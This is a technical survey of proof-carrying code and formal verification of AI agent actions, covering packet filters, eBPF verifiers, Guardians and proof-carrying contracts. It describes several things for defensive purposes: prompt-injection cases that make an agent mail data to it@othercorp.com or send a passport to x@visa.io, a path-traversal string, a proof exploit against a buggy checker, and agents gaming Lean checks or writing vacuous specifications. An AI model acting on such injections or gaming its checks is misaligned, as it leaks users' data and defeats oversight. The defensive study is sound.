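Suppose a filter needs the word that starts 64 bytes into the packet. Some packets are too short to have one, so the filter first checks the length:

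```
    SUBQ r2, 72, r4    r4 = length - 72
    BLT  r4, L1        if r4 is negative, go to L1
    LDQ  r5, 64(r1)    r5 = word at address r1 + 64
L1: RET                return
```

The generator works backwards from the last line. The policy requires nothing of a filter that returns, so the condition for `RET` is simply "true". The read adds the condition $\mathrm{rd}(r_1 \oplus 64)$. The branch can go either way, so its condition covers both cases:

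$$(r_4 < 0 \Rightarrow \text{true}) \,\land\, (r_4 \ge 0 \Rightarrow \mathrm{rd}(r_1 \oplus 64))$$

For the subtraction, the generator replaces $r_4$ with $r_2 \ominus 72$. It then adds the precondition, $Pre$. Without the part that is trivially true, the obligation is that for all contents of the registers and memory

$$Pre \Rightarrow (r_2 \ominus 72 \ge 0 \Rightarrow \mathrm{rd}(r_1 \oplus 64))$$

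The proof is short. If the length minus 72 isn't negative, the length is more than 64. Since 64 is a multiple of 8, the precondition with $i = 64$ permits the read.

Without the length check, the producer would have to prove that the filter may read this word in every packet. The producer couldn't prove this, because the precondition allows packets as short as 64 bytes. A filter that reads the word at offset 8 needs no length check, because every packet is long enough.

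### Four filters and their speed

Necula and Lee wrote four filters by hand in assembly language for the DEC Alpha processor. The sizes in the table include the proof, which was about three times as large as the code.

| Packets the filter accepts | Instructions | Size | Time to check the proof |
|---|---|---|---|
| All IP packets | 8 | 385 bytes | 0.78 ms |
| IP packets from one network | 15 | 516 bytes | 1.07 ms |
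| IP or ARP packets between two networks | 47 | 1,024 bytes | 2.35 ms |
| TCP packets to one port | 28 | 814 bytes | 1.71 ms |

Their theorem prover, which they call a toy, found each proof in 5 to 10 seconds, but a programmer sometimes had to give it a new fact about arithmetic.

In tests on 200,000 packets recorded from a busy network at Carnegie Mellon University, the filters ran about ten times as fast as the same filters in BPF. They were also about 25% faster than filters protected by software fault isolation, which inserts checks into machine code before memory accesses. *Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997) reported that the filters were twice as fast as filters written in the safe part of the Modula-3 language.

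The kernel checks each proof only once. For the TCP filter, the time saved in filtering made up for the time spent checking the proof after 1,200 packets compared with BPF, and after 28,000 compared with fault isolation. At the network's average of about 1,000 packets per second, that is about one second for BPF and half a minute for fault isolation.

Much of the tenfold gain over BPF probably came from replacing an interpreter with hand-tuned machine code. The comparison with fault isolation better measures what the proofs saved, because both versions used the same assembly code. A 25% gain is useful in a kernel, but it would hardly matter for an agent, which spends far longer waiting for its model.

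### Why the method stayed narrow

None of the four filters contains a loop. To prove anything about a loop, the producer needs an invariant, a statement that holds on every pass through it. Necula and Lee also certified a 39-instruction checksum routine that ran twice as fast as the kernel's own version. But they had to write its loop invariant by hand, and they considered invariants the main obstacle to generating proofs automatically.

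The method can express policies that go beyond memory safety. In one example, a filter-like program may change an entry in a kernel table only if a tag next to the entry isn't zero. Necula and Lee also suggested requiring a program to release any lock it takes. Someone must still find the proofs, and Necula doubted that the approach would scale to large programs. He expected more from compilers that turn a source program's type safety into a proof about the machine code. This works for memory safety because the types already contain most of the argument. Types usually don't express rules about locks or table entries, so the compiler can't use them to prove that a program follows those rules.

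Proofs can also become very large. The condition to be proved for a branch includes the conditions for both paths. If the paths rejoin, the condition for the rest of the program appears in both, so ten such branches in a row can produce up to 1,024 copies of it. This didn't happen with the small filters, and a programmer can limit it by adding invariants that split the program into pieces.

The kernel must trust the policy and the generator as well as the checker. The precondition above permits an eight-byte read at offset 64 of a 65-byte packet, although seven of those bytes lie beyond the packet's end. If the kernel stored something private there, a filter with a valid proof could read it. A false axiom would be worse, and Necula admits choosing the axioms for arithmetic "a bit haphazardly". The generator can also be large. Appel (2001), in *Foundational Proof-Carrying Code*, cites a later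 system whose generator had 23,000 lines of C. A bug in the generator could make the recipient check a proof of the wrong statement.

### Appel's version without a generator

Appel's answer was to remove the generator and define safety directly in terms of what the processor does. Let $s$ be the contents of the machine's registers and memory, and let $s \mapsto s'$ mean that one instruction takes the machine from $s$ to $s'$. If an instruction would break the policy, for example by reading a forbidden address, the definition gives it no next state. A state is then safe if the program can never get stuck after it:

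$$\mathrm{safe}(s) \iff \forall s'.\; (s \mapsto^{\ast} s' \Rightarrow \exists s''.\; s' \mapsto s'')$$

The star stands for any number of steps. The producer must prove this, along with any rules about types that the proof uses, from basic logic and arithmetic. The recipient has to trust only the proof checker, the policy and the description of the processor. Describing a large part of the Sparc processor took about 1,600 lines of logic.

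The smaller trusted base required much more proof. By 2001, Appel's group had about 30,000 lines of machine-checked proofs but only a tentative way to handle data that a program changes after creating it. The paper that combined all the pieces appeared in 2010, according to Princeton University's *Foundational Proof-Carrying Code*.

### Cheaper checks in Java and Linux

When Necula and Lee published their experiment, Java already offered an easier compromise. A Java compiler produces bytecode, instructions for a virtual machine, and a verifier checks the bytecode's types before it runs. This check establishes some of what a proof would, without extra effort from programmers. But the types can't express a policy like the rule about tagged table entries. Appel adds that Java's guarantee also depends on the verifier, the compiler that turns bytecode into machine code, and the garbage collector,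 which reclaims unused memory.

Linux took another route with eBPF, a successor to BPF that lets users extend the kernel in many more ways. *Keel* (Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte, 2026) explains that the kernel's own verifier analyses each program, so the programmer doesn't have to supply a proof. If the verifier can show that the program is safe and will finish, the kernel compiles it to machine code.

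The verifier is part of the trusted base, and Nelson, Wang and Torlak (2021), in *A proof-carrying approach to building correct and flexible BPF verifiers*, point to bugs in it that could let malicious programs through. It also rejects some safe programs, because it tracks a range of possible values for each register but not how registers relate to each other. Cai and colleagues give the example of a program that writes two records one after the other into an 800-byte buffer. The first record takes up $u$ bytes, where $u$ is between 0 and 800, and the second gets the remaining $800 - u$. The second record can't go past the end, because

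$$u + (800 - u) = 800$$

The verifier has established only that the starting position and the length are each between 0 and 800. Within those bounds, the second record could end at byte 1,600, so the verifier rejects the program.

### Proofs return to the kernel

The developers of ExoBPF tried to bring proof-carrying code back for eBPF, but their proofs became very large and they gave up the project. Sun (2025), in *bpf*, a set of proposed changes to Linux, asks for proofs only where the verifier gets stuck. The kernel then sends out a formula stating that the program reaches this point and breaks the rule. For the buffer, the formula is

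$$0 \le u \le 800 \;\land\; u + (800 - u) > 800$$

A solver outside the kernel proves that no value of $u$ makes this true, and the kernel checks the proof, which is 852 bytes here. With such proofs, the kernel accepted 403 of 512 programs it had previously rejected. The largest proof was 8.4 MB and took up to about three seconds to check. The solver has over 500,000 lines of code, but the kernel has to trust only the checker, which has about 5,000.

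Even the checker could not be trusted without proof, since Cai and colleagues found 13 bugs in it. One of its rules for comparing products did not account for computer arithmetic wrapping around. In signed 8-bit arithmetic, for example, 64 times 2 is −128. The rule therefore let a proof derive a false statement, from which any other statement follows. The team built a 13-step proof that the checker accepted for any formula, so an attacker could have used it to get an unsafe program past the checker.

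Their replacement, Keel, comes with a proof in Lean that it accepts a certificate only if the formula cannot be satisfied. It is also 1.3 times as fast. The proofs that its C code meets the specification and runs within bounded time and memory come to about 65,000 lines. The researchers developed them with Claude Code and Google's Gemini 4 Argon, so AI may be reducing the work that limited the use of proof-carrying code. But Keel still relies on the eBPF verifier, the kind of component Appel wanted to eliminate, to produce the right formula.

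### Proofs that come with access requests

*Proof-Carrying Authentication* (Appel and Felten, 1999) applied the idea to requests for access instead of code. For example, if a publisher lets students at certain universities read its journals, a student could send a proof that combines the publisher's rule with her university's signed statement that she is enrolled. The paper's logic is general enough to represent several existing access-control systems, but that generality means no procedure can decide every request automatically. The requester therefore supplies the proof, and the server only checks it. The proof would still be valid if the university had certified someone wrongly.

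Bauer, Schneider and Felten built a working system on this idea and described it in *A General and Flexible Access-Control System for the Web* (2002). An agent's tool call is also a request, and some recent systems similarly attach proofs to tool calls.

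## Guardians: verifying a whole plan before it runs

The kernel can check all of a packet filter before running it, because the filter is a complete program. An ordinary agent has no complete program to check, because its model chooses each tool call after seeing the result of the last one. Meijer, a programming-language designer, proposes that the model write a whole workflow in advance. A verifier checks the workflow against a policy, and an interpreter runs the workflow only if it passes. Nada Amin and other contributors have built Guardians, an open-source verifier for such workflows.

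### Names in place of data

If Michelle asks her agent to fetch and summarise her email, the model writes a plan like this one, shown here in a shorter notation than Meijer's:

```
emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize_emails(emails)
return summary
```

Here `emails` is a symbolic name for a value that doesn't exist yet. As in CaMeL, the model writes the plan before the agent fetches any mail, so a hostile email can't add a step. Meijer compares prompt injection to SQL injection, where an attacker types a database command into a form field and the database runs it. Developers prevent SQL injection by keeping commands separate from values, and the plan also separates them. A hostile email can still distort the summary, as in the dual-LLM pattern.

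The plan itself may also be harmful. In one of Meijer's examples, the attacker controls the description of the mail-fetching tool, which the model reads before it plans. The description falsely claims that compliance rules require the agent to send out a summary, so the model adds a line before the last one:

```
send_email(to: "it@othercorp.com", body: summary)
```

A policy against this specifies a source (the result of `fetch_mail`), a sink (the body of `send_email`) and a condition (the recipient is outside Michelle's company). The verifier traces the variables and finds that `summary` comes from `emails`, `emails` comes from `fetch_mail`, and the new line puts `summary` into a message to another domain. It rejects the plan before the agent has fetched any mail. Meijer suggests using existing tools such as CodeQL and Semgrep for this analysis.

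FIDES could also block this message, but only after the agent had read the inbox. The drawback of checking earlier is that some values aren't available yet. If Michelle wants the summary sent to whoever wrote the latest email, the verifier has to treat the recipient as a possible outsider. The plan could pass if it checked the address first and sent the summary only to colleagues.

### Deleting two files

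Meijer's second example has no attacker. A user asks the agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The deletion tool accepts patterns, and the model takes a shortcut:

```
delete_file("*.txt")
```

This deletes every text file in the directory. To catch the mistake, the verifier needs a postcondition, a statement of what must be true after the plan has run. Let $F$ be the set of files before the run and $F'$ the set afterwards. The obvious postcondition for the task is

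$$\text{foo.txt} \notin F' \;\land\; \text{bar.txt} \notin F'$$

The shortcut satisfies it, since both files are gone. What's missing is a frame condition, which states what must stay unchanged. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described the underlying difficulty, the frame problem, in 1969. Meijer adds a frame condition to the tool, so that a call with pattern $p$ leaves all other files alone:

$$\forall f \notin \mathrm{glob}(p).\; (f \in F' \Leftrightarrow f \in F)$$

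Here $\mathrm{glob}(p)$ is the set of file names that match the pattern. Meijer writes that the shortcut then fails to verify, but this condition isn't enough. A file called `notes.txt` matches `*.txt`, so the tool may delete it, and the plan still meets the postcondition for the task. The task needs a frame condition of its own:

$$\forall f \notin \{\text{foo.txt}, \text{bar.txt}\}.\; (f \in F' \Leftrightarrow f \in F)$$

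Now the verifier can reject the shortcut, with a directory that contains `notes.txt` as the counterexample. It still needs the tool's frame condition to accept the correct plan, which deletes the two files one at a time. Without that condition, the verifier couldn't rule out that deleting `foo.txt` also removes `notes.txt`, so it would reject the correct plan too.

Both frame conditions concern only which files exist. A plan that emptied `notes.txt` without deleting it would pass, so a complete condition would also have to cover the files' contents.

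An operator can write the rule about outgoing mail once for all tasks, but every deletion request needs its own postcondition. In the talk *Return of the Theorem* (2026), Meijer has software translate the user's question into a formal specification before the model plans. If the translation omits the frame condition, the verifier will approve a plan that deletes `*.txt`, and the proof will still be valid.

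### The open-source verifier

clauz3's *Background And Related Work* describes how Guardians implements the proposal. An operator writes the policy and a specification for each tool. Taint rules handle flows such as the one from the inbox to an outside address. A rule can name sanitizers, which are steps that make data acceptable for the sink, so whoever chooses them decides what counts as safe to release. Guardians also applies security automata, which Meijer presents as runtime monitors, to the plan before it runs.

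For preconditions, postconditions and frame conditions, Guardians uses Z3, a program that searches for values that make a formula true. The verifier asks for a case in which the plan breaks the rule. If Z3 shows that there is none, the plan passes. Meijer illustrates this with a car dealer's chatbot that a customer had persuaded to sell a car for $1. The dealer's rules define a set of permitted sales, the agent's plan defines the set of sales it could make, and the verifier checks that

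$$\text{Plan} \subseteq \text{Permitted}$$

A sale at $1 is in the first set but not in the second, so the plan fails. The dealer must first write down, in a formal language, the lowest price for each model.

Meijer's *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls* (2026) describes a version closer to proof-carrying code, in which the model supplies a proof along with the plan. Guardians instead relies on Z3, which is much larger than a simple proof checker. It also relies on the tool specifications, the policy and the interpreter that runs the plan.

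clauz3 is itself a verifier, for Python programs that agents write, and it mostly avoids frame conditions. It works out a list of every effect the program can have, and any effect that isn't on the list can't happen. A contract that permits email only to Bob therefore excludes every other recipient. This works only for effects that clauz3 tracks. The agent proposes the contract and the user decides whether to accept it, whereas in Guardians the operator sets the policy.

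The published case for Guardians relies on worked examples rather than benchmark scores. clauz3's *Guardians Synergies* proposes turning Michelle's inbox into a shared test for the two verifiers.

### Tasks the model can't plan in advance

According to Zhou and colleagues, Guardians and CaMeL both require an agent to plan before it reads, a constraint that ELBA avoids. The constraint is serious for open-ended work, because an agent can't plan the repair of a failing program before it has read the error message. clauz3's developers list the method's suitability for coding agents as an open question, and CaMeL's failure on AgentDyn suggests that the problem isn't limited to code.

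Branches help if the planner can foresee the possibilities. "If three o'clock is free, book it, otherwise propose four" is a complete plan, and a verifier can check both outcomes. *Agentproof* (2026) checks workflow graphs this way. It combines the graph with a finite-state machine that represents a rule, then searches every path for a violation. Some frameworks let agents change the graph during a run, for example by adding another agent, and the new graph then has to be checked too. But no manageable set of branches covers every edit that a broken program might need.

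Runtime checks can handle facts that the verifier doesn't know or that may change. A calendar slot may fill up after the agent first looks at it, so *Agents as Software* (2026) recommends checking again just before the agent creates the event. Meijer accepts runtime checks for whatever a verifier can't settle. But these checks bring back the risk of a half-finished run, which static verification was supposed to remove. A plan can reduce that risk by making its checks before the first irreversible step, although the facts may change again after the checks.

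The third reply is to plan again. Meijer argues that code is now so easy to generate that a system can discard any plan it can't prove safe and ask for another. This works when the plan was badly written, but a model that lacks information won't write a better one just by trying again. It has to run one plan and read the results before writing a second.

The verifier can check the second plan against the same policy, so a ban on all mail to outsiders would still hold. But the model has now read untrusted data, so an attacker can influence any choice the policy doesn't restrict. The source-and-sink rule also gets weaker. If the first plan returned Michelle's summary to the model, the model could copy the text into the second plan as a constant, and the verifier couldn't trace it to `fetch_mail`. To prevent this, the system would have to carry labels from one plan to the next, as FIDES does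 with its context label.

It is unclear how much these replies recover. Meijer expects writing a plan first to improve a model's reasoning, but acknowledged in 2025 that nobody had formally measured the effect. *FAOPs* (2026) cites one favourable figure from Lean4Agent, which verifies workflows in Lean and reports about 12% higher task success for verified workflows. This figure doesn't show how planning ahead compares with an ordinary agent loop.

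### Proving the framework instead of the plan

Guardians checks every plan but relies on the agent framework, the software that runs the plan, working correctly. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) proves properties of the framework once, and they hold for any action the model requests. The model can still choose each step after receiving the previous result, so the objection about planning doesn't apply.

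Moon and Varshney applied the method to PocketFlow, a minimal open-source framework. A PocketFlow agent is a graph of steps. Each step returns an action, and a loop follows the edge labeled with that action to the next step. They verified a version of this loop in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, and Dafny's compiler translated it into Python.

The proof represents the model as a function without a body. Dafny can assume only that this function returns a value of type `Action`, which has four variants, so the proof has to cover every such value in any order.

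A boundary event represents an effect on the outside world, such as reading a file. If the loop refuses an action, the event records that nothing happened. A policy is a condition

$$\Pi(s, a, e, s')$$

on the state before a step, the model's action, the resulting event and the state afterwards. PocketFlow's policy permits reads only inside a workspace directory, calls only to tools on an allowlist, and steps only up to a fixed limit.

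The proof uses two descriptions of the framework. An abstract model $M$ is simple enough for Dafny to prove that it always obeys the policy. The implementation model $I$ follows the real loop in more detail. Refinement means that $M$ can match everything $I$ does. They start in matching states, and from any pair of matching states

$$s_I \xrightarrow{\;a,\,e_I\;} s_I' \quad\Longrightarrow\quad s_M \xrightarrow{\;a,\,e_M\;} s_M'$$

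for some event $e_M$ that matches $e_I$ and some state $s_M'$ that matches $s_I'$. Step by step, every run of $I$ therefore has a counterpart in $M$ with the same actions. The counterpart obeys the policy, and the last part of the proof shows that $I$ then obeys it too.

Like the ETAS theorems, the guarantee holds only if every outside effect passes through the verified software, a condition Moon and Varshney call effect exclusivity. Giving the agent a general shell tool would make the guarantee almost worthless. *Tether* (2026) avoids this assumption by watching the calls that programs make to the operating system, so it can monitor arbitrary shell commands. On two coding benchmarks, it caught every violation and raised false alarms in 2.3% to 5.0% of cases, counting only runs whose actions it can model.

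PocketFlow's three rules are also weak. If `send_email` is on the allowlist, the loop will send Michelle's summary to the attacker, because the policy checks only the tool's name. The rule for reading files requires the path to start with the workspace directory. If the rule only compares text, `/workspace/../secrets.txt` passes even though it points outside that directory. ELBA's file library resolves such paths before checking them.

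A stricter policy could restrict recipients, since $\Pi$ may refer to an action's arguments. But Moon and Varshney acknowledge that no policy of this form can require an answer to be truthful or forbid a message that deceives its reader, because that depends on what the text means. Such policies also can't enforce noninterference, and neither can runtime monitors. Guardians has the advantage when a rule depends on the task. It can allow this plan to delete only `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, while a fixed policy for the framework would probably have to permit deletion in general.

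Claude models wrote the specifications and proofs, using 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens per run, and Dafny checked each path through the graph in at most 2.5 seconds. Someone still has to read the specifications, as one result shows. The second test agent could open only documents on an approved list, but the policy template had a field for tool calls and none for documents. When the model had access to the agent's source code, it left the tool-call field empty. Dafny then proved that every recorded tool call was on the allowlist, which was true because no tool calls were recorded, and no rule restricted the documents. The specification also passed three automatic checks, including one meant to catch empty specifications.

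### Skills that come with evidence

Many agents can load skills, which are folders of instructions and scripts, often written by strangers. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) proposes that a skill come with evidence that it uses only the capabilities it declares, such as reading files but not opening network connections. The evidence includes an analysis of the scripts, a type check of the code that carries out tool calls, and a search for violations in sequences of calls up to a set length. The agent's software repeats these checks when it starts, so it doesn't have to trust the skill's author.

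Metere's theorem assumes that the script analysis never misses an effect, but the published implementation scans for known patterns, so it could miss an effect that no pattern matches. A skill could also pass every check and still lead the agent to reveal private data in a chat message, because sending one requires no capability.

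## Proof-carrying contracts: a proof for every tool call

Guardians needs a complete plan before it can verify anything. With proof-carrying contracts (PC2), an agent proves one tool call at a time, so it can read each result before choosing the next call. In the design described in *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, 2026), a formal contract states what must hold throughout a task, and the agent attaches to each call a Lean proof that the call will keep the contract. A program called the Airlock checks the proof and runs the call only if the proof is correct. As with the packet filters of 1996, the untrusted side, here the agent, has to find the proof.

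A person can use PC2 to bind their own assistant, which may make mistakes or obey an injected instruction. A client can also use it to hire an agent run by another company, which the client can't inspect and whose interests may differ from the client's. The Airlock can then hold the company's fee and release it once the agent proves it has finished the job.

### The travel contract

In the paper's main example, a family hires a travel agency's agent to book hotels for three nights and obtain a visa. The agent may commit at most 2,000 EUR, including fees. It may send the passport only to the consulate, and it may book only hotels with a recorded rating of at least 7 out of 10. If $x$ stands for the records of the task, the contract requires at every moment that

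$$x.\mathrm{spent} \le 2000 \;\land\; x.\mathrm{discl} \subseteq \{\mathrm{consulate}\} \;\land\; \forall (h,n,m) \in x.\mathrm{booked}.\; x.\mathrm{rating}(h) \ge 7$$

Here $x.\mathrm{discl}$ is the set of recipients who have been sent the passport, and each booking consists of a hotel $h$, a night $n$ and an amount $m$. The ratings come from what the paper calls an expert, here a language model whose prompt both parties fix when they sign. The Airlock holds the passport and the agency's 300 EUR fee. It pays the fee when the agent proves that it has booked all three nights and that the consulate has granted the visa. If the consulate refuses the visa or 30 days pass, the family gets the fee back.

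In a sample session, the expert gives Hotel Aurora an 8, and the agent asks to book the first night for 900 EUR. It has committed no money yet, so the booking stays within the budget, and the rating is high enough. The agent can therefore prove that the call keeps the contract, and the Airlock makes the booking. Two more nights at 500 EUR each would bring the total to

$$900 + 500 + 500 = 1900 \le 2000$$

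so the agent could prove those calls too. If the third night cost 700 EUR, the total would be 2,100 EUR and no valid proof would exist.

The agent then downloads its email and finds a message, supposedly from the visa office, that tells it to send the passport to x@visa.io. The agent obeys and calls the sending tool. The address isn't the consulate's, so the statement the agent has to prove is false, and the Airlock rejects the call. The Airlock doesn't need to recognise the message as an attack, and it would reject the same call if the agent had made the address up.

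### What the agent has to prove

Each tool comes with a model of its possible effects. Write $D_T(i, s, s')$ if the model says that calling tool $T$ with input $i$ in state $s$ could lead to state $s'$, either during the call or at its end. The agent may see only part of the state, called its view. In the travel contract, for example, the view hides the contents of the passport. If $C$ is the condition that the contract imposes and $v$ is the agent's view, the proof obligation is

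$$\forall s.\; \big(\mathrm{View}(s) = v \land C(s)\big) \Rightarrow \Big(\exists s'.\, D_T(i,s,s') \;\land\; \forall s'.\, \big(D_T(i,s,s') \Rightarrow C(s')\big)\Big)$$

where $s$ ranges over the states in which the contract is active. Whatever the hidden parts of the state are, if the contract holds now, it must also hold in every state that the tool model allows. The part with $\exists$ requires the model to allow at least one state. Without it, an agent could trivially prove that all outcomes of a call are acceptable when the model doesn't cover the call at all. Designers can also use this part to add preconditions. The model of the payment tool, for instance, allows no outcome unless the agent has reached its goal, so the agent must prove the goal to get the fee.

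Suppose the model of the booking tool allows two outcomes for the second night at the Aurora. Either the hotel refuses and nothing changes, or the total rises from 900 to 1,400 EUR and the booking appears in the records. The proof has to show that the three conditions hold in both cases, which Lean's existing automation can do.

Finding and checking a proof takes time, and the state may change meanwhile. The Airlock therefore keeps running a control routine, which at each step waits, corrects a problem or ends the contract. Each request specifies how many of these steps may pass before the call runs, and its proof must cover every state they could lead to. If more steps pass, the request expires.

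The Airlock writes the proof obligation itself, from the contract, the tool models and the view it recorded. If the agent wrote the statement, it could change Lean's notation so that a trivial truth looked like the real obligation. Ciliberto and colleagues cite a case where agents exploited a Lean submission system this way.

### Is an invariant easier to write than a policy?

Most systems that check tool calls use a permission policy, which specifies the calls an agent may make. In PC2, the parties instead write an invariant, a condition that must always hold, and the agent works out which calls preserve it. Ciliberto and colleagues argue that an invariant is often easier to write than a permission policy. For example, it is easy to say that a car must not crash, but much harder to list every situation in which braking or steering would cause a crash.

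A policy may also forbid harmless actions. A cap of 600 EUR per night would keep three nights within the budget, but it would reject the plan that costs 900, 500 and 500 EUR. Ciliberto and colleagues prove that any safe rule based on the same view and tool models permits only calls whose PC2 obligation is true.

For the travel contract, this advantage is small. A developer could replace the cap with a rule that existing commitments plus the new amount must not exceed 2,000 EUR, which ordinary code could check without a proof. Ciliberto and colleagues accept that a policy can enforce the exact rule if someone derives it and a program can decide it. Proofs are more useful when no program can decide every case, or when deriving the rule takes a lot of reasoning.

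In those cases, however, the invariant may be hard to write too. PC2 requires the control routine to be able to preserve the invariant from every state that satisfies it. Suppose a company lets an agent run cloud jobs on a budget of 100 EUR. The jobs cost up to 30 EUR an hour, and stopping them takes up to 20 minutes. The obvious invariant, a bill of at most 100 EUR, doesn't work. At 95 EUR it still holds, but stopping the jobs could add another 10 EUR. Ciliberto and colleagues therefore reserve money for the shutdown:

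$$b + r h \le B$$

Here $b$ is the bill, $r$ the highest hourly cost, $h$ the time needed to stop and $B$ the budget. With these numbers, the bill may be at most 90 EUR while the jobs are running at full cost. The contract "the car hasn't crashed" has the same problem, because it is true of a car driving at full speed one metre from a wall. The contract's author would have to describe the states from which the car can still stop in time, which is a large part of the analysis that PC2 was supposed to avoid. The agent still has more freedom than under a fixed policy, but the author may not save much work.

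### The commitment and completion theorems

The commitment theorem states that $C$ holds at every moment from the contract's start until it closes, whatever calls and proofs the agent submits. This follows by induction because $C$ holds at the start, the control routine preserves it, and every call that runs has a proof that the call preserves it too.

The completion theorem covers contracts with a goal and a payment, like the family's. Such a contract ends in at most one of three ways:

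- It never starts, because the starting conditions don't hold.
- The agreed payment procedure runs, from a state in which the agent has reached the goal.
- The agreed termination procedure runs, for example because the deadline is near.

Another theorem shows that if a contract has a deadline, either payment or termination begins by that deadline. Once the Airlock has accepted the proof, the family can't veto the payment. The agency needs a proof to collect the payment. The theorems don't guarantee that the agent will finish its task or that a bank will complete the transfer.

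Both theorems need the first four assumptions in this table. The other three extend the guarantee from the Airlock's records to the outside world, and to any agent.

| Assumption | What it requires |
|---|---|
| Sound checking | The proof checker accepts only true statements |
| Coverage | Each tool model includes every state that a real call can reach |
| Initialisation and control | The contract holds when it starts, and the control routine preserves it |
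| Execution integrity | The Airlock follows its algorithm and runs exactly the call that the agent proved |
| Fidelity | The records remain true of the outside world |
| Adequacy | True records that satisfy the contract imply the protection that the parties specified |
| Isolation | The agent can affect the system only through calls that the Airlock runs |

None of these assumptions requires the agent to be honest or competent. The parties can examine the tools and the Airlock once and then use them with any agent.

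### When the records don't match the world

Suppose the agent has booked three nights for 1,900 EUR, and a hotel then adds a 150 EUR fee that the tool model doesn't include. The records still show 1,900 EUR, but the family has paid 2,050 EUR, even though every proof was valid.

Ciliberto and colleagues show how to design a payment tool that prevents this. The Airlock first records the most that a payment may cost, then asks a payment provider for a single-use virtual card with that limit. For each payment $j$, let $a_j$ be the amount charged, $u_j$ the card's limit and $r_j$ the amount recorded. Then

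$$a_j \le u_j \le r_j$$

Adding up all the payments shows that the total charged is at most the total recorded, which the contract keeps within 2,000 EUR. The hotel can't collect its extra fee unless the card's limit covers it. This works if the provider enforces the limits, but then a single card with a 2,000 EUR limit would protect the budget without any proofs.

Bookings are harder to guarantee. A genuine confirmation shows that the booking service sent it, but the hotel may still cancel the room. If the contract's goal requires only recorded confirmations, the agency could collect its fee for a trip that later falls through.

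The paper's general answer is to make each such assumption explicit. The parties can then prove it under stated conditions, make someone responsible for it, reduce the risk with tests or monitoring, or accept the risk. Developers can also package a tool with its model and proofs as a "capability module", so that other contracts can reuse the work. With a list of these assumptions, the family can find out who is responsible for a cancelled room, but they still need somewhere to stay. Ciliberto and colleagues themselves argue that breaches should be prevented because compensation can't undo every harm.

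### Ratings that count as true

In the sample session, the agent first tries to book Hotel Belvedere, which pays the agency a commission. The hotel has no rating yet, so the Airlock rejects the call. The agent then asks the expert for a rating and gets a 5. It asks again to try to get a better one, but gets the same recorded 5.

Recording the answer means the agent can't keep asking until random variation produces a 7. But the rating model can still be wrong. A hotel could write its description to inflate its rating, or hide an instruction in it. The contract would then accept an undeserved 8, because the proof establishes only that the recorded rating is at least 7.

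Ciliberto and colleagues suggest testing experts on misleading examples before signing a contract, fixing what evidence they receive, and specifying when new evidence justifies another rating. They acknowledge that someone still has to evaluate how well this works. The budget and passport clauses hold even if an attacker controls the agent's model, but the rating clause protects the family only as well as another language model resists manipulation.

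### Keeping the agent inside the Airlock

If the agent could log in to the payment account directly, it could spend money without a proof. The Airlock therefore runs the agent in a sandbox that has no access to the Airlock's files or credentials. Before signing, both parties can use remote attestation to check which software is running, based on signed evidence from the hardware.

The sandbox may need one network connection, to the company that runs the agent's model. In the travel contract, the agent can read the emails it downloads. If its model runs on the agency's servers, the agency receives those emails without any tool call or proof. The passport's contents wouldn't leak this way, because the Airlock never shows them to the agent. Ciliberto and colleagues say the parties must decide whether the model's provider may see the data. If not, they can run the model on a machine they control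 or on hardware that keeps the computation confidential.

### Contracts that leave something out

The travel contract's formula doesn't mention a destination, so the agent could book three hotels in three cities and still collect its fee. It could also choose the most expensive hotel within the budget because that hotel pays it a commission. Protecting clients from an agent with other interests is one of the main reasons for PC2, but this contract protects them only through the budget and the rating. An injected email recommending such a hotel would also succeed, because PC2 doesn't track whose text influenced a choice.

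Ciliberto and colleagues give a similar example, in which a contract requires a flight and a hotel but not matching dates. They propose a "formalizer agent" that would draft the contract, explain it in ordinary language and search for outcomes the contract allows but the parties might not want. This seems sensible, because most families would find it easier to reject a trip with mismatched dates than to notice what is missing from a formula. Reviewed templates could also help with common kinds of contract. They leave developing and testing these ideas to future work.

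### Lean proofs but no live agents

The project's code repository contains Lean definitions and checked proofs of results from the paper, with their assumptions, and documents the implementation. The paper doesn't list which theorems Lean has checked but refers readers to the repository. Lean can check that the conclusions follow from the assumptions, but not that a payment provider respects its limits or that a sandbox has no vulnerabilities.

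Ciliberto and colleagues report no measurements with live agents, so nobody yet knows how much PC2 would reduce an agent's utility. The travel session is a constructed example with simplified proofs. They say a future evaluation should measure whether agents find proofs in time, how many requests expire, and how much useful work gets done with what resources.

*LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) offers some indirect evidence, because it also checks tool calls with Lean, although the agent writes no proofs. Developers write a policy in Lean, and a proof establishes in advance that the checking program applies the policy correctly. On τ²-bench, five Qwen models without LEANGUARD made at least 33 calls that the policy forbids. With it, no forbidden call ran. When agents also received the reason for each blocked call, they completed 70.9% of tasks, compared with 72.7% without LEANGUARD.

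The guard interfered with harmless tasks much more on DTap, a benchmark for prompt injection. The share of harmless tasks completed fell from 53.1% to 12.5%, while the success rate of direct attacks fell from 57.9% to 5.9%. Agents had no permission to change anything in this test, so they couldn't complete tasks that required a change.

Sankar and colleagues also tested an automatic search for permitted alternatives to blocked calls. Of 252 calls blocked because of their arguments, the search found a permitted version of 88 and proved each one acceptable, in a median time of 2 milliseconds. This suggests simple proofs like the one for the Aurora booking would take little computing time. The test gives little evidence about contracts that need harder reasoning, for which PC2 would be most useful.

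### Certificates that record approval

Wang (2026), in *Proof-Carrying Agent Actions*, uses the word "proof" for evidence about an action and how someone authorised it. Companies run agents on many platforms, and publishing a document might appear as a shell command on one and a tool call on another. Wang proposes a certificate that has the same form everywhere. For an action $a$, it contains

$$\mathrm{Cert}(a) = (E(a),\, Q_r(a),\, Q_h(a),\, P(a),\, I(a))$$

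- $E$ describes the action, including who requested it, whose account the agent used and where any data went.
- $Q_r$ contains receipts from the software that ran the action.
- $Q_h$ contains human approvals.
- $P$ contains what a reviewer needs to replay the decision.
- $I$ contains integrity references, such as cryptographic commitments, that help reveal later changes to the record.

The system fills in the certificate at five checkpoints. It compares the action with the policy, opens a record, stores the agent's assumptions, waits for approval if the policy requires it, and records the outcome. For the Aurora booking, a certificate could show that the agency's agent requested the room, a parent approved the request, and the hotel confirmed the booking.

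The certificate also records whether an approval could have stopped the action. On some platforms the evidence arrives only after the action, and Wang labels those cases "observe-only". The label is useful because a reader might otherwise assume that a recorded approval could have prevented the action.

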